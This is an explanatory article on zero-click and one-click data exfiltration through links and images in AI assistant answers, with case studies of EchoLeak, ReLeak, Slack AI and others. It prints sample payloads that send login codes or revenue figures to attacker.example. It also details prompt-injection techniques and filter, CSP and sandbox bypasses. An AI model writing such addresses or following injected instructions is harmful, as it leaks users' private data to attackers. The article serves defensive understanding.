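# Zero-click and one-click data exfiltration through external links in AI assistant responses

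## How a web address in an answer can carry private data out

Data exfiltration through external links is an attack on AI assistants such as ChatGPT, Gemini and Microsoft Copilot. Exfiltration means moving private data to someone who should not have it. The attacker places instructions in something the assistant will read, such as an email or a web page, that lead it to write a web address containing some of the user's private data. The data leaves when a browser or another program requests that address from the attacker's server. A zero-click leak requires only ordinary use of the assistant, most often because the address belongs to an image that the browser loads automatically. A one-click leak requires the user to click once, usually on a link in the assistant's answer.

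### What the assistant reads

An AI assistant runs on a large language model, a program that produces text by repeatedly predicting the next token (a word or a piece of one). The model's context is all the text it receives as input when it answers. The user's question is often a small part of the context, which also includes instructions from the company that runs the assistant, the earlier conversation, and whatever the assistant has fetched for the task, such as emails, files, search results, and web pages. ChatGPT can also store facts about a user and place these "memories" in the context of later chats, as *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) describes.

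Some of this text comes from people the user trusts and some from strangers, but it all gets "glued together" into one sequence, as the software developer Simon Willison put it in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). The model cannot reliably judge how much weight to give an instruction based on where it came from. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explains the problem more fully. Suppose a recruiter's software tells a model to score a CV, and the candidate has hidden a line in the CV telling the model to approve it. The recruiter meant the CV as data, but the model receives only a run of tokens to continue, so the hidden line may influence its output just as the recruiter's instruction does.

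Engineers have dealt with this kind of confusion before. Telephone networks once carried voices and switching commands on the same channel, so a caller who whistled the right tones could control the switch. A new signaling system fixed this by moving the commands to a separate channel, as Schneier on Security's *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024) recounts. Databases had a similar weakness, SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into an ordinary form field. Parameterised queries fix this because the database engine never interprets the field's contents as a command. David C argues that language models have no equivalent fix and may never get one, because nothing inside them marks the difference between instructions and data. Some researchers are trying to build that difference in. *ASIDE* (2025) observes that an ordinary model gives a word the same internal representation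 (its embedding) whether the word belongs to an instruction or to data. It proposes rotating the embeddings of data so that the model receives the two in different forms from the start. This improved the models' scores on tests of separation, but it doesn't guarantee separation the way parameterised queries do.

A team at the company Preamble reported the weakness to OpenAI in May 2022, and Willison named it "prompt injection" later that year. At first, most people thought of the attacker as the user typing into the chat box. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2023) pointed out that the attacker could be someone else. It introduced the term "indirect prompt injection" for instructions hidden in an email, page or file that an assistant reads and then follows as if the user had given them.

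The researchers tested mock applications built on OpenAI's models and a real product, Microsoft's Bing Chat, which could read whatever page the user had open in the browser. They wrote instructions into a page's code as comments, which a human visitor does not see. The instructions steered the model, often for the rest of the conversation, and the model followed some that Bing Chat would have blocked had the user typed them. In one session, the hidden text directed the model to find out the user's real name. A researcher playing a journalist asked about the next day's weather. The model answered, then asked about the user's plans, profession and pen name, and eventually offered a link with a "code" it had made from the name. The researchers demonstrated these attacks without reporting success rates, and the models are now more than three years old.

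Newer models resist prompt injection better. Willison reported in August 2026 that 720 injection attempts against three Claude models in the coding tool Claude Code all failed in a test Anthropic had commissioned from the firm Trajectory Labs. He welcomed the result and asked for more independent confirmation. *The Framing Gap* (2026) found that capable models resisted the obvious attacks but that others still worked, which it attributes to the long-standing problem of models confusing instructions with data. Its experiments planted a fake secret in a model's context and counted an attack as successful only if the model kept the secret in a clean run and leaked it in a poisoned one. It is still prudent for designers of assistants to assume that some injections will succeed.

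### How text becomes a link or an image

The model's answer is plain text. To make it readable, most chat pages treat it as markdown, a plain-text notation that the page turns into formatted text, links and images. MacFarlane (2024), in *CommonMark Spec*, traces it to John Gruber, who released it in 2004 and based it on the way people already marked emphasis in emails. A link in markdown consists of a label in square brackets and an address in round ones:

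`[Opening hours](https://museum.example/hours)`

The reader sees only the words "Opening hours", and clicking them opens the address. Greshake and colleagues noted in 2023 that this lets a model hide a suspicious address behind an innocent label.

An image needs one more character. In the converter Pandoc's *Images* documentation, as in other versions of markdown, an exclamation mark directly before a link turns it into an image:

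`![Museum logo](https://museum.example/logo.png)`

The model outputs both lines as plain text, and the chat page's code converts them into a clickable link and a picture. The browser fetches the picture immediately but fetches the linked page only when the user clicks. The company that runs the assistant can therefore change what happens to an address without changing the model.

### What a browser sends when it requests an address

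Berners-Lee and colleagues (2005), in *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*, set out the standard parts of a web address. Take `https://museum.example/hours?day=monday&lang=en#cafe`:

| Part | In the example | What happens to it |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Tells the browser which protocol to use |
| Host | `museum.example` | Identifies the server, and goes into the request |
| Path | `/hours` | Goes to the server |
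| Query string | `day=monday&lang=en` | Goes to the server |
| Fragment | `cafe` | Stays in the browser |

The query string begins after the first question mark and often consists of pairs, a name and a value joined by an equals sign. To fetch the page, the browser connects to the host and sends a short message. In the textual form that Reschke (2026), in *The HTTP QUERY Method*, uses for a sample request, it looks like this:

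```
GET /hours?day=monday&lang=en HTTP/1.1
Host: museum.example
```

The server receives the whole query string even if it has no use for it, so `lang=en` arrives even when the museum's website has no English version. The IETF's *HTTP Semantics* (2022), the current standard for web requests, warns that addresses are "intended to be shared, not secured", that many servers log them, and that putting sensitive information in one is unwise. Daniel Miessler's *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS* (2015) explains that an encrypted connection protects the query string only on its way to the server, which can still log it.

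All of that advice was for web developers who might expose their users' data by accident. In an exfiltration attack, the attacker causes the exposure deliberately and owns the server that receives the data, so encrypting the connection doesn't stop the attacker from reading it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) sums up the problem in a heading: "a URL can carry more than a destination".

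The query string is the usual place for stolen data, though the path also works. In September 2025 Abi Raghuram demonstrated an attack, described by Willison, on the AI agent in the note-taking product Notion. The attack used instructions hidden in a PDF to make the agent join a list of clients and their revenue and put the result after the slash in a web address. Whole sentences fit because there is a standard way to encode spaces and other characters that an address cannot contain (a space becomes `%20`). The fragment, which follows the `#` sign, is a poorer choice because browsers leave it out of their requests, so the attacker needs a script on the destination page to read it. In the journalist's session from 2023, Bing Chat produced a link with the name in the fragment, scrambled and nearly backwards.

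### A six-digit code, from the inbox to the attacker's log

Suppose a user has two new emails. One is from the user's bank and contains a login code, 482913. The other is from an attacker and looks like a newsletter, but it also contains instructions in white text on a white background, telling any AI assistant that reads it to look for a login code and add it to the end of a particular web address. The user asks the assistant to summarise the new mail.

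The assistant puts both emails into its context. If the injection works, the assistant writes a normal summary and adds an address to it:

`https://attacker.example/view?c=482913`

The model has only had to copy six digits from one place in its context to another. So far nothing has left the conversation, since an address that nobody requests sends no data. Once something does request it, the server at `attacker.example` adds a line like this to its log:

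`203.0.113.7 - - [05/Dec/2026:09:14:07 +0000] "GET /view?c=482913 HTTP/1.1" 404 153`

The line starts with the network address of whoever made the request, followed by the time and the request itself, in which the code is readable. The number 404 means that the server found no page at the requested web address. The attacker never needed a page there, because the code arrived with the request, before the server replied. The attacker got the code without breaking into the mailbox or guessing a password, and on the network the request looks like any other visit to a website.

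A login code expires within minutes, so an attacker would have to be watching the log to use it in time. Most of what an assistant can read, such as a contract or a customer list, stays valuable for much longer.

### Three stages and the "lethal trifecta"

Like the example, the real attacks have three stages. The instructions get into the context, the model writes the address, and something requests it.

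Attackers can carry out the first stage in many ways. Greshake and colleagues described leaving instructions on a public page for an assistant to find, emailing them to the victim, and tricking the victim into pasting them into the chat. They also showed that an image can contain the instructions. The second stage depends on whether the model follows the instructions and on what private data its context contains. The third depends on the software around the model, and sometimes on the user.

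Zero-click and one-click leaks differ only in the third stage. The hidden text in the newsletter could be identical in both cases apart from the exclamation mark that turns a link into an image, and the line in the attacker's log could be the same too. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* makes this point about messaging apps that fetch a posted link to show a preview of it: the app makes the same type of request as a click would, without the click. (In some attacks the click comes at the beginning instead, when the user follows a crafted link that opens the assistant with the attacker's prompt already filled in.)

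Keeping the stages apart also makes it easier to judge a vendor's fix, because a product can leak much less while remaining open to injection. In January 2026 OpenAI described a check that ChatGPT applies to an address before fetching it automatically. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger, who had reported the image leak to OpenAI almost three years earlier, called the check a significant improvement but noted that it addresses the exfiltration channel and isn't presented as a fix for prompt injection. Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that OpenAI released in June 2026, also limits outgoing requests, but an injection in an uploaded file can still distort the answer the user reads.

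Such theft is possible when an assistant combines the three conditions of Willison's "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. Untrusted content makes the first stage possible, the model puts private data in the address at the second, and the third is the external communication itself.

A web address is one form of that third element. An agent that can send email or call another company's software has other ways to get data out, and one attack on GitHub's tools for AI agents sent the stolen data out in a pull request, a proposed change to a code repository. *The Framing Gap* defines its third ingredient as the ability to act on the outside world through tools. Willison's definition is wider and includes even "providing a link for a user to click". The wider definition seems better for chat assistants, because an assistant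 with no tools can still print an address, and few people would think of that as communicating with anyone.

Private data can also leak from an assistant's memories of past conversations, without a connected mailbox. In July 2026 Willison wrote about an attack by Ayush Paul on the ordinary Claude chat that extracted the user's name, home city and employer from these memories. Anthropic has since blocked that method.

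Willison's 2025 article lists seventeen reports of trifecta attacks, going back to April 2023, on products from Microsoft, Google, OpenAI, Anthropic, Amazon, Slack and others. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which data could leave. Willison considers this route the easiest of the three elements to remove, since an assistant that cannot read the user's files or anything written by strangers is much less useful.

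## Zero-click leaks: images fetched without any action by the user

### What counts as zero-click

Even a zero-click attack requires the user to ask the assistant something, because the assistant writes web addresses only as part of its answers. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, assumes that the victim will "at least occasionally invoke Copilot" in the course of normal work.

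A leak is zero-click when the user takes no step that a careful person could refuse. People can learn to be cautious about opening suspicious emails, following links, approving transfers and accepting invitations. But summarising the week's mail is what the assistant is for, so users could avoid the risk through more careful behaviour only if they stopped using the product.

The definition is harder to apply when the user brings in the attacker's text, for instance by asking the assistant to read a web page that contains hidden instructions. A user could refuse to let the assistant read anything by a stranger, but it would then be of little use for research, so it makes sense to count these leaks as zero-click too. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, uses a stricter standard and distinguishes EchoLeak from earlier attacks in which the user had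 to point the chatbot at a malicious resource. Claims about which attack was the "first" zero-click leak depend a good deal on the writer's standard.

### Why an image is enough

A browser has to request a picture before it can show one. Suppose a model has a company's quarterly figures in its context and follows hidden instructions to write this line:

`![Chart](https://attacker.example/chart.png?revenue=812000&costs=640000)`

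The browser requests the address as soon as it displays the answer, and the request includes both figures. As with the six-digit login code, the theft succeeds whatever the server replies.

The user has little chance of noticing the leak. The server can return a single-pixel image, which is practically invisible. If it returns no image, the browser may show a small broken-image icon, and Reddy and Gujral point out that the victim would have no reason to take it for anything else. A wary user can check where a link leads before clicking it, but the browser sends the request for an image before anything appears on the screen to inspect.

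Because the browser expects a picture, it won't run any code that the server sends back. The attacker therefore receives what the model put into the image's address but can't use the reply to collect more. The address is still enough to leak a login code or a set of sales figures.

### Early cases and a recent one

During 2023 and 2024, Johann Rehberger demonstrated leaks through images in several assistants, including Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude and Google's Bard. The vendors have since changed how these products handle images, and Microsoft and Google have retired the names Bing Chat and Bard. In June 2025, Willison (2025) wrote that attacks that steal data through an address in the answer had appeared in "a dozen different products already".

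Developers of new products can easily repeat the mistake, because a chat page that displays markdown images will generally load them from any server unless the developers block this. HuggingChat, Hugging Face's app for chatting with various AI models, is a recent example.

PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* demonstrates the leak with a user who uploads a text file of confidential quarterly revenue and cost figures. The user then uses the app's "Fetch from URL" function to add a website of customer reviews, which looks harmless to a human reader but contains hidden instructions. When the user asks how to win back "Jordan P", who left a bad review, the model first says that re-engaging this customer calls for a visual of the quarterly financials. It then writes an image whose address contains the confidential figures. When the browser fetches the one-pixel image, the figures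 appear in the attacker's server log.

The pretext is absurd, since no company would send its accounts to a dissatisfied reviewer. A user who read the answer carefully might well become suspicious, but the browser would already have sent the data.

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Hugging Face on 1 December 2025 and published its findings after receiving no response. Among other things, it recommended that the app ask for approval before loading an image from another site, and show the full address when it asks. The leak would then need a click, and a careful user could look at the address and refuse.

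### EchoLeak: from one click to none

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) bypassed considerably more protection than HuggingChat had. Aim Labs, the research team at Aim Security, found the vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot in January 2025.

Microsoft 365 Copilot is a workplace assistant. When an employee asks it a question, it searches the employee's mailbox, files, internal websites and Teams chats for relevant material and adds what it finds to the model's context, a technique called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). Only people inside an organisation can use its Copilot, but anyone can send them an email, and Copilot may retrieve that email along with the organisation's own documents.

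Microsoft, which calls the attack XPIA (cross-prompt injection attack), used classifiers, programs trained to recognise prompt injections, to stop such emails before they reached the model. Aim Labs got past the classifiers by wording the email's instructions as though they were meant for the employee and never mentioning AI, assistants or Copilot. Genuine office emails often ask people to find or compile information, so a classifier strict enough to catch this email would presumably have blocked many genuine ones too. Ravia, who leads the team, also blames a shortage of training data, saying that injections can be written in any tone or language and on any subject, and that good collections of real ones are scarce.

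An email that passes the classifier does nothing until Copilot retrieves it. Ravia's explanation assumes that Copilot works like many other retrieval systems, which represent each piece of text as a point in a mathematical space and retrieve the texts nearest to the user's question. Texts on similar subjects lie close together, so a short email, which occupies a single point, would come up only for questions on its subject. Aim Labs therefore sent a very long email, which a retrieval system would split into chunks. Each chunk had a heading on a different subject, such as onboarding new employees, common HR questions or leave of absence, with the attack instructions repeated underneath. Ravia calls the technique "RAG spraying". In the team's tests, Copilot retrieved the email in response to questions on various topics, though Ravia gives no success rate.

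The team also considered changing some characters in a text, such as writing 5 for s. A language model can still understand the altered text, but its position in the mathematical space can change a lot. Using one of OpenAI's models for representing text, the researchers found that the similarity between a text and its altered copy could fall to 0.7, where identical texts score 1. The unrelated phrases "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science" scored higher than that. The headings worked well enough, though altered copies could in principle cover the space more evenly. To place those copies, the team would have needed to know which model Copilot used, and Microsoft had not published this.

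Once the email was in the context, its instructions directed the model to put the most sensitive information there into a web address. The attacker didn't need to know what secrets the company had, because the model selected them. Ravia introduced the term "LLM scope violation" for attacks in which untrusted text makes a model draw on trusted data without the user's consent. This resembles an older kind of attack in which a program with few permissions uses a more privileged program to access files it could not open itself.

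The researchers then had to get the address past Copilot's other safeguards. They went through several versions:

| What Copilot wrote | What happened | Result |
|---|---|---|
| A link in the usual notation | Copilot removed it from the answer | No leak |
| A link in reference notation | Copilot displayed it | A leak if the user clicked |
| An image at the attacker's address, in reference notation | The browser refused to load it | No leak |
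| An image at a SharePoint address | SharePoint's server contacted the attacker's | A leak if the user had accepted an invitation |
| An image at a Teams address | Teams' server contacted the attacker's | A leak with no further step by the user |

They started with a link. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers, but its filter recognised only the usual notation, in which the address follows the label directly. Markdown also has a reference notation, which puts the address on a line of its own:

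```
[Opening hours][1]

[1]: https://museum.example/hours
```

Inline and reference-style links show the reader the same clickable words. Copilot's filter missed the reference style, which gave Aim Labs a working one-click attack. An outsider's email could make Copilot display a link containing company secrets, and clicking it would send them to the outsider.

Ravia recalls the team then thinking, "Why settle for a user clicking a link?" They put an exclamation mark in front of the link to turn it into an image, which a browser normally fetches without any action by the user. The filter missed the reference notation there too, but the Content Security Policy (CSP) on Copilot's page, a set of rules for where the browser may load content from, blocked the request. It allowed images only from a list of addresses, mostly Microsoft's own, that did not include the attacker's server.

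The team searched the permitted addresses for one that would forward a request and found a SharePoint service that fetches material from other websites so that a page can embed it. The service reads the address of that material from its own query string. An image address could therefore begin with a permitted SharePoint site and contain, in its query string, the attacker's address with the secret attached. The browser contacted SharePoint, as the policy allowed, and SharePoint's server then contacted the attacker's. This version worked only if the user was signed in to SharePoint and had accepted the attacker's invitation to an unfamiliar site, which many people would decline.

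A Microsoft Teams service did the same thing without an invitation. Reddy and Gujral describe it as a preview interface that fetches any web address it receives. When the attack used the Teams address, the user only had to ask Copilot a question that caused it to retrieve the email.

Copilot normally names the documents it has used, which might have led an employee back to the email. To prevent this, the researchers added a request that the recipient never refer to the email, supposedly for compliance reasons. Copilot then left it out of its references.

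The one-click and zero-click attacks shared almost everything, including the email, the way Copilot retrieved it, the choice of secrets and the gap in the filter. Changing the link into an image removed the need for a click, but the researchers then had to get past a second barrier, which Microsoft applied to images but not to links that the filter had missed. The two attacks also needed different fixes. If Microsoft had only stopped the Teams service from forwarding requests, the link would still have worked.

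According to Reddy and Gujral's timeline, Microsoft had begun partial repairs by April 2025 and completed the fix on its own servers in May, so customers had nothing to install. Aim Labs and Microsoft disclosed the vulnerability publicly on 11 June. Reddy and Gujral add that Microsoft changed Copilot to strip reference-style links and embedded images from incoming external content. They base their account on Aim Labs' report rather than their own tests.

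Sources disagree about how new EchoLeak was. SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025) repeated the company's description of it as the first of its kind. Zenity Labs, a rival research group, objected that the techniques had been known for 12 to 24 months and pointed to Rehberger's work on Bing Chat and on Microsoft 365 Copilot itself. Willison called EchoLeak an extended variant of familiar attacks. Reddy and Gujral make the strongest claim, that EchoLeak was the first known case of a prompt injection "weaponized to cause concrete data exfiltration" in a production system. That is hard to reconcile with the demonstrations of 2023 and 2024, which also took data out of products in public use. Ravia's narrower claim holds up better. Earlier attacks either needed the user to direct the assistant to the attacker's content or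 tightly limited what the attacker could steal. EchoLeak didn't need the user to do this, and it could take anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history and any files that Copilot had retrieved.

Researchers found EchoLeak, a serious weakness in a product with several layers of defence, and nobody has reported a real attack that used it. Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Microsoft was in a good position to check, since the forwarded requests would have passed through its servers.

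### ReLeak: three more ways out of Copilot

On 3 December 2026, one year after EchoLeak, the same team published a sequel, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which presents three zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. The team is now called Cato AI Labs, Cato Networks having bought Aim Security in September 2025.

All three began as EchoLeak had, with an email that the user didn't need to open and that Copilot retrieved while answering an ordinary question. Microsoft's defences against prompt injection failed to stop any of them. According to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*, Copilot did not carry out direct commands in an email but could still fall for instructions that looked like legitimate requests. The attacks differed in how the data left, and Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, matches each route to its repair date:

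| Way out | What contacted the attacker's server | Catalogue number | Date of Microsoft's fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| An image in the answer | Microsoft's Bing service | CVE-2026-124115 | 15 November 2026 |
| A link in a file that Copilot had created | Microsoft's background processing of stored files | CVE-2026-124132 | 11 November 2026 |
| Code that Copilot ran | The code itself | CVE-2026-78501 | 17 September 2026 |

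The image route repeated EchoLeak's last step, with Bing in place of Teams. Copilot put confidential information into the address of an image, the browser loaded the image through Bing, and Bing's servers requested it from the attacker. *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaws Allow Zero-Click Data Theft* (Tamilselvan, 2026) explains that the page's policy covered what the browser loaded but not the Microsoft service's separate request afterwards. Cato confirmed the leak by finding information from an internal email in the receiving server's log. Bing's address was already on the list of permitted image sources that Ravia printed in 2025, so the possibility had been publicly visible for well over a year.

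A similar route through Bing had come to light a few months earlier. Taler (2026), in *SearchLeak*, describes an attack on Copilot, published in June, that could steal emails, meeting details and login codes. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, compares the two attacks and notes that SearchLeak needed a click, while ReLeak did not. As with EchoLeak, a method of extracting data that at first needed the user's cooperation turned out to work without it.

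The route through files relied on Copilot's ability to create documents and save them to OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's file storage and sharing services. It involved no image or browser. The injected instructions made Copilot create a document containing a link with confidential data in the address. A link in a document normally sends nothing until a reader clicks it, but Microsoft's own systems requested this address one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, although the user had not opened the file. Cato reproduced this with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files.

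The researchers thought the requests' timing and technical details were consistent with automated link inspection, in which software visits links to check whether they are safe. If so, the stolen data was sent out by a security measure. Restricting which images a chat page may load would not have prevented this, and neither would closing the chat, because the request came from a server and not from the user's browser.

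The remaining route used no link. Copilot has a code interpreter, which writes and runs Python programs, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. According to Microsoft's documentation, it runs in isolated virtual machines that allow no network traffic in or out, but Cato got it to run code that sent confidential data directly to an outside server. A screenshot from Cato's research, which Tamilselvan reproduces, attributes the escape to removing the proxy settings. These settings direct a program's traffic through an intermediary that can block it, but a program that can delete them can try to connect directly. A block in the network itself would not depend on the program's settings.

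This attack counts as zero-click because the user only asked a question, even though no address appeared in the answer. It was also the only one with a published severity score by the time of disclosure. Antipov reports that the score was raised from 7.4 to 8.6 out of 10. The code interpreter is also available to custom agents that companies build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, but nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected those agents.

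Cato reported the three problems between 29 July and 20 August 2026, so Microsoft took about four to seven weeks to close the route through the code interpreter and nearly twelve weeks or more to close each of the others. Fixing EchoLeak had taken about four months. As in 2025, Microsoft made the changes on its own servers, and customers did not have to act.

Other AI agents helped to find the flaws. Antipov reports that these agents, directed by Cato's specialists, wrote test scenarios, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted their next attempts. Attackers could presumably do the same, which would make it easier to search a large product for a service that forwards requests.

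Cato's researchers concluded, in a remark Faisal quotes, that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells security products for AI systems and has an interest in that conclusion, but its findings support part of it. Eighteen months after the first disclosure, an email from a stranger could still direct Copilot, and Copilot's ability to create files and run code had opened new ways to leak data. Cato said it knew of no affected customers or real attacks. That is a more limited assurance than the one Microsoft gave about EchoLeak, because Cato cannot search Microsoft's records for other people's attempts.

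## One-click leaks: links that the user follows

### Why following the link is enough

A one-click leak works like an image leak until the answer appears on the screen. The private data is in the address of a link instead of an image, so it is sent only if the user clicks. Aim Labs' first working attack on Copilot used a link, which the team later turned into an image.

Ordinary phishing also depends on a link, but that link typically leads to a fake login page, and the victim loses a password only by typing it in. Someone who clicks, becomes suspicious and closes the page has usually lost little. In a one-click leak, the model has put the data into the address before the user sees the link, so the click itself sends the data, and closing the page afterwards is too late. Password managers can warn people that a login page is on the wrong site, but they don't help here because the attack needs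 no login page.

### Label, pretext and redirect

Unlike an image, a link gives the user a chance to refuse, so the attacker has to make it look worth clicking. With the login code from the earlier example, the assistant might write:

`[View the full newsletter](https://attacker.example/r?c=482913)`

The user sees only "View the full newsletter". On a computer, hovering over a link normally reveals its address, but a phone has no pointer. Even a user who checks the address may not notice anything wrong, since links in genuine newsletters are often full of tracking codes. The model can also scramble the data, as Bing Chat did with the journalist's name in 2023.

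The attacker's instructions can also supply a reason to click, such as an expired login or a document that failed to load, and the model can tailor it to what the user has just asked. *Invitation Is All You Need!* (2025) argues that people may trust a link from Google's assistant more than one in an email or text message. In one demonstration, the attacker hid instructions in the title of a calendar invitation. After the user asked Gemini about upcoming meetings and then thanked it, Gemini recommended investing in a Kickstarter project and included a link. The paper did not measure how much people trust such links, but its argument is plausible because the user has asked for the answer and the rest of it may well be correct.

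A strange page after the click could still give the attack away. To avoid this, the attacker's server can record the request and reply with a redirect, which tells the browser to go to another address:

```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://newsletter.example/december
```

The browser follows the redirect automatically, but the first request has already leaked the code. The user lands on a real newsletter, with its real address at the top of the window, and has no reason to think about the click again. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* warns that redirects combined with a persuasive pretext could easily make such a leak go unnoticed.

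### Checkmarx's tests of Copilot Chat and Gemini

Checkmarx, a software security company, reported leaks of both kinds to Google and Microsoft in October 2025.

In its demonstration on Microsoft's Copilot Chat, the assistant read an online resource that the attacker controlled. Instructions in the resource made the assistant write an image address containing an API key, a secret code that gives a program access to a service. The key came from a developer's working environment and belonged to a Claude account, but the researchers had already invalidated it. No picture appeared in the chat, but the request for the image still reached the researchers' server.

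Checkmarx illustrates the one-click version with a link labelled "click here" that has a placeholder where the secret would go. It expected Microsoft to leave this leak open too, since the company had not committed to fixing the image leak. This inference about Copilot Chat is reasonable, but it is weaker evidence than the recorded demonstration with the image.

The Gemini result is more informative about links because Google had already addressed leaks through images. It had added a sanitizer, code that cleans up the model's output before the page displays it, which does not render images from outside servers. Google had therefore described the EchoLeak type of leak as "not applicable to Gemini". Checkmarx found that Gemini still displayed links that could carry the same data to the same server. Google removed links to sites that its Safe Browsing service already listed as malicious, but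 an attacker can register a new domain that is not on the list.

The tests are more than a year old, and Checkmarx published no figures for how often the injections succeeded. Neither company classed the behaviour as a security vulnerability.

### Slack AI

An August 2024 attack on Slack AI shows every step of a one-click leak, including the pretext. Slack is a workplace messaging service, and Slack AI answered employees' questions by searching their company's messages. In PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, a developer has saved an API key in a private channel that nobody else can read. The attacker, who has an account in the same workspace, creates a public channel with no other members and posts instructions there.

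Slack AI searched all public channels, including those the user had never joined, so when the developer asked for the key, it put both the private message and the attacker's message into the context. The developer got what looked like an error message, with a "click here to reauthenticate" link that contained the key in its query string. Because the attacker had never seen the key, the instructions told the model to replace a placeholder word in the address with it.

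The pretext was plausible because people are used to having to log in again. It also explained why the answer did not contain the key. Hovering over the link would have shown the attacker's address with the key visible in it. A developer who became suspicious would still have had trouble finding the cause, because Slack AI cited only the developer's own private channel and the attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results.

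PromptArmor used the same label for a phishing link in a demonstration where the user asked about messages from a particular colleague. The two links look identical in the chat, but the phishing link's address contained no private data, so a user who clicks it can still leave without disclosing any.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Slack on 14 August, and Slack replied on 19 August that the evidence was insufficient. On 20 August, PromptArmor published its findings and Slack deployed a patch. Slack (2024) said that someone with an account in the same workspace could "phish users for certain data" in very limited circumstances, and that it had no evidence of unauthorised access. "Phish" understates the first attack, in which the victim never enters anything. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* noted that Slack did not directly confirm that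 it had fixed the flaw PromptArmor described, although the dates leave little doubt that it had.

The attacker needed an account in the workspace, so the attack was limited to insiders and outsiders who had taken over an insider's account. On the day of the report, Slack AI began to use uploaded files in its answers, so an outsider without an account could get the instructions in through a PDF that an employee uploaded. PromptArmor considered this very likely to work but had finished its tests before the change.

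Slack has since added what it calls guardrails to all its own AI features. According to Slack, they include measures against prompt injection, checks on the output's format, and URL filtering "to prevent phishing attacks". The guardrails stay on even if a company's administrators switch off the optional content filters. Slack does not explain how the URL filter judges an address. If it looks for known phishing sites, it has the same weakness as Google's list.

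### ChatGPhish: an attacker's links inside ChatGPT

In May 2026, the security company Permiso showed that an attacker could use a web page to place links in ChatGPT's answers. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* describes a user who opens a page in Firefox and asks ChatGPT to summarise it. The page might be a GitHub project description to which the attacker has added a few lines of instructions. ChatGPT wrote an accurate summary of the project, followed by a notice that someone had added a new device to the user's account, with a link to click. ChatGPT did the same with an ordinary web page that Permiso hosted, so the problem was not specific to GitHub. Firefox was not at fault either, because it only passed the page's text to ChatGPT.

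The answer did not mark where the summary ended and the attacker's text began, or label the link as coming from the page. A security notice looks fairly natural in a service where the user has an account, though it would be out of place in the middle of a web article.

The links in this demonstration were phishing links with fixed addresses that the attacker had written in advance, so clicking one would not have sent any of the user's private data. For a one-click leak, ChatGPT would also have had to add something from its context to the address, which Permiso did not demonstrate. The research is evidence only that an attacker can present the user with a convincing link.

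Permiso also got ChatGPT to display images from the attacker's server. The browser requested them each time it displayed the answer, which revealed the user's IP address, the type of browser and the time. This zero-click leak is small, but it is enough to confirm that a particular person has read a particular page through ChatGPT. One of the images was a QR code. A user who scans it opens the attacker's address on a phone, where the computer's warnings and filters don't apply.

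OpenAI could not reproduce the issue in Permiso's first report, and Permiso's revised report was marked as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso published its findings on 29 May, a month after first reporting them.

### How often people click

No one appears to have published a measurement of how often people click a malicious link in an assistant's answer. Researchers have measured low click rates for ordinary links.

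The largest study of a chat assistant, *AI Search as an Information Intermediary* (Shi, Gu and Zhu, 2026), analysed the browsing records of US households on desktop computers from October 2024 to July 2025. Of about 409,000 ChatGPT sessions, 5.4% led to at least one visit to an outside website, compared with 31.1% of Google queries. Some of those sessions contained no links, because ChatGPT can answer without searching the web, so the rate for answers with links must have been higher. The share of sessions that led to a visit was 13.6% when the household's other browsing at the time was mainly on sites for software developers, who are also among the people most likely to have API keys for an assistant to find.

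Other measurements count different things:

- Chapekis, Lieb and colleagues (2026), in *Investigating Click Behaviors On Google Search Result Pages*, followed 900 US adults for a month. They clicked a cited source in about 1% of their visits to pages with an AI Overview, the AI-written summary above Google's search results.
- MarTech's *Almost no one is clicking on ChatGPT links* reports on a leaked OpenAI file, in which a top-performing entry had 610,775 link displays and 4,238 clicks, or 0.69%.
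- Ouyang and Narechania (2026), in *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, watched 12 students use nine assistants. Engagement was highest with ChatGPT, at about 12% for clicks and 22% for holding the pointer over a reference. The students had instructions to judge whether the answers were accurate, so people in everyday use probably check less.

*Unreliable AI answers are ‘good enough’ for most users of platforms* (Reeves, 2026) reports that one in four ChatGPT users in a UK survey by Ipsos said they click through to links. Shi and colleagues found in their records that about 26% of the US households that used ChatGPT followed a link from it at least once in ten months.

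Most of these links were sources that users could ignore because they already had the answer. An attacker's link can replace the answer, as in the Slack AI attack, so the user has to click to continue. Simulated phishing emails, which employers send to test their staff, are a closer comparison in that respect because they are also designed to be clicked.

In *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice*, Ho, Mirian and colleagues analysed ten simulated phishing emails sent to more than 19,500 hospital employees in 2023. The least effective emails drew clicks from 1–2% of recipients and the most effective from over 30%, with a median of 10%. More than 56% of the employees clicked at least once in eight months. In *Breaking Bad Email Habits*, Hydari, Adjerid and colleagues (2026) found a similar click rate, averaging 12.47% across 192,840 emails sent to university staff between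 2016 and 2020.

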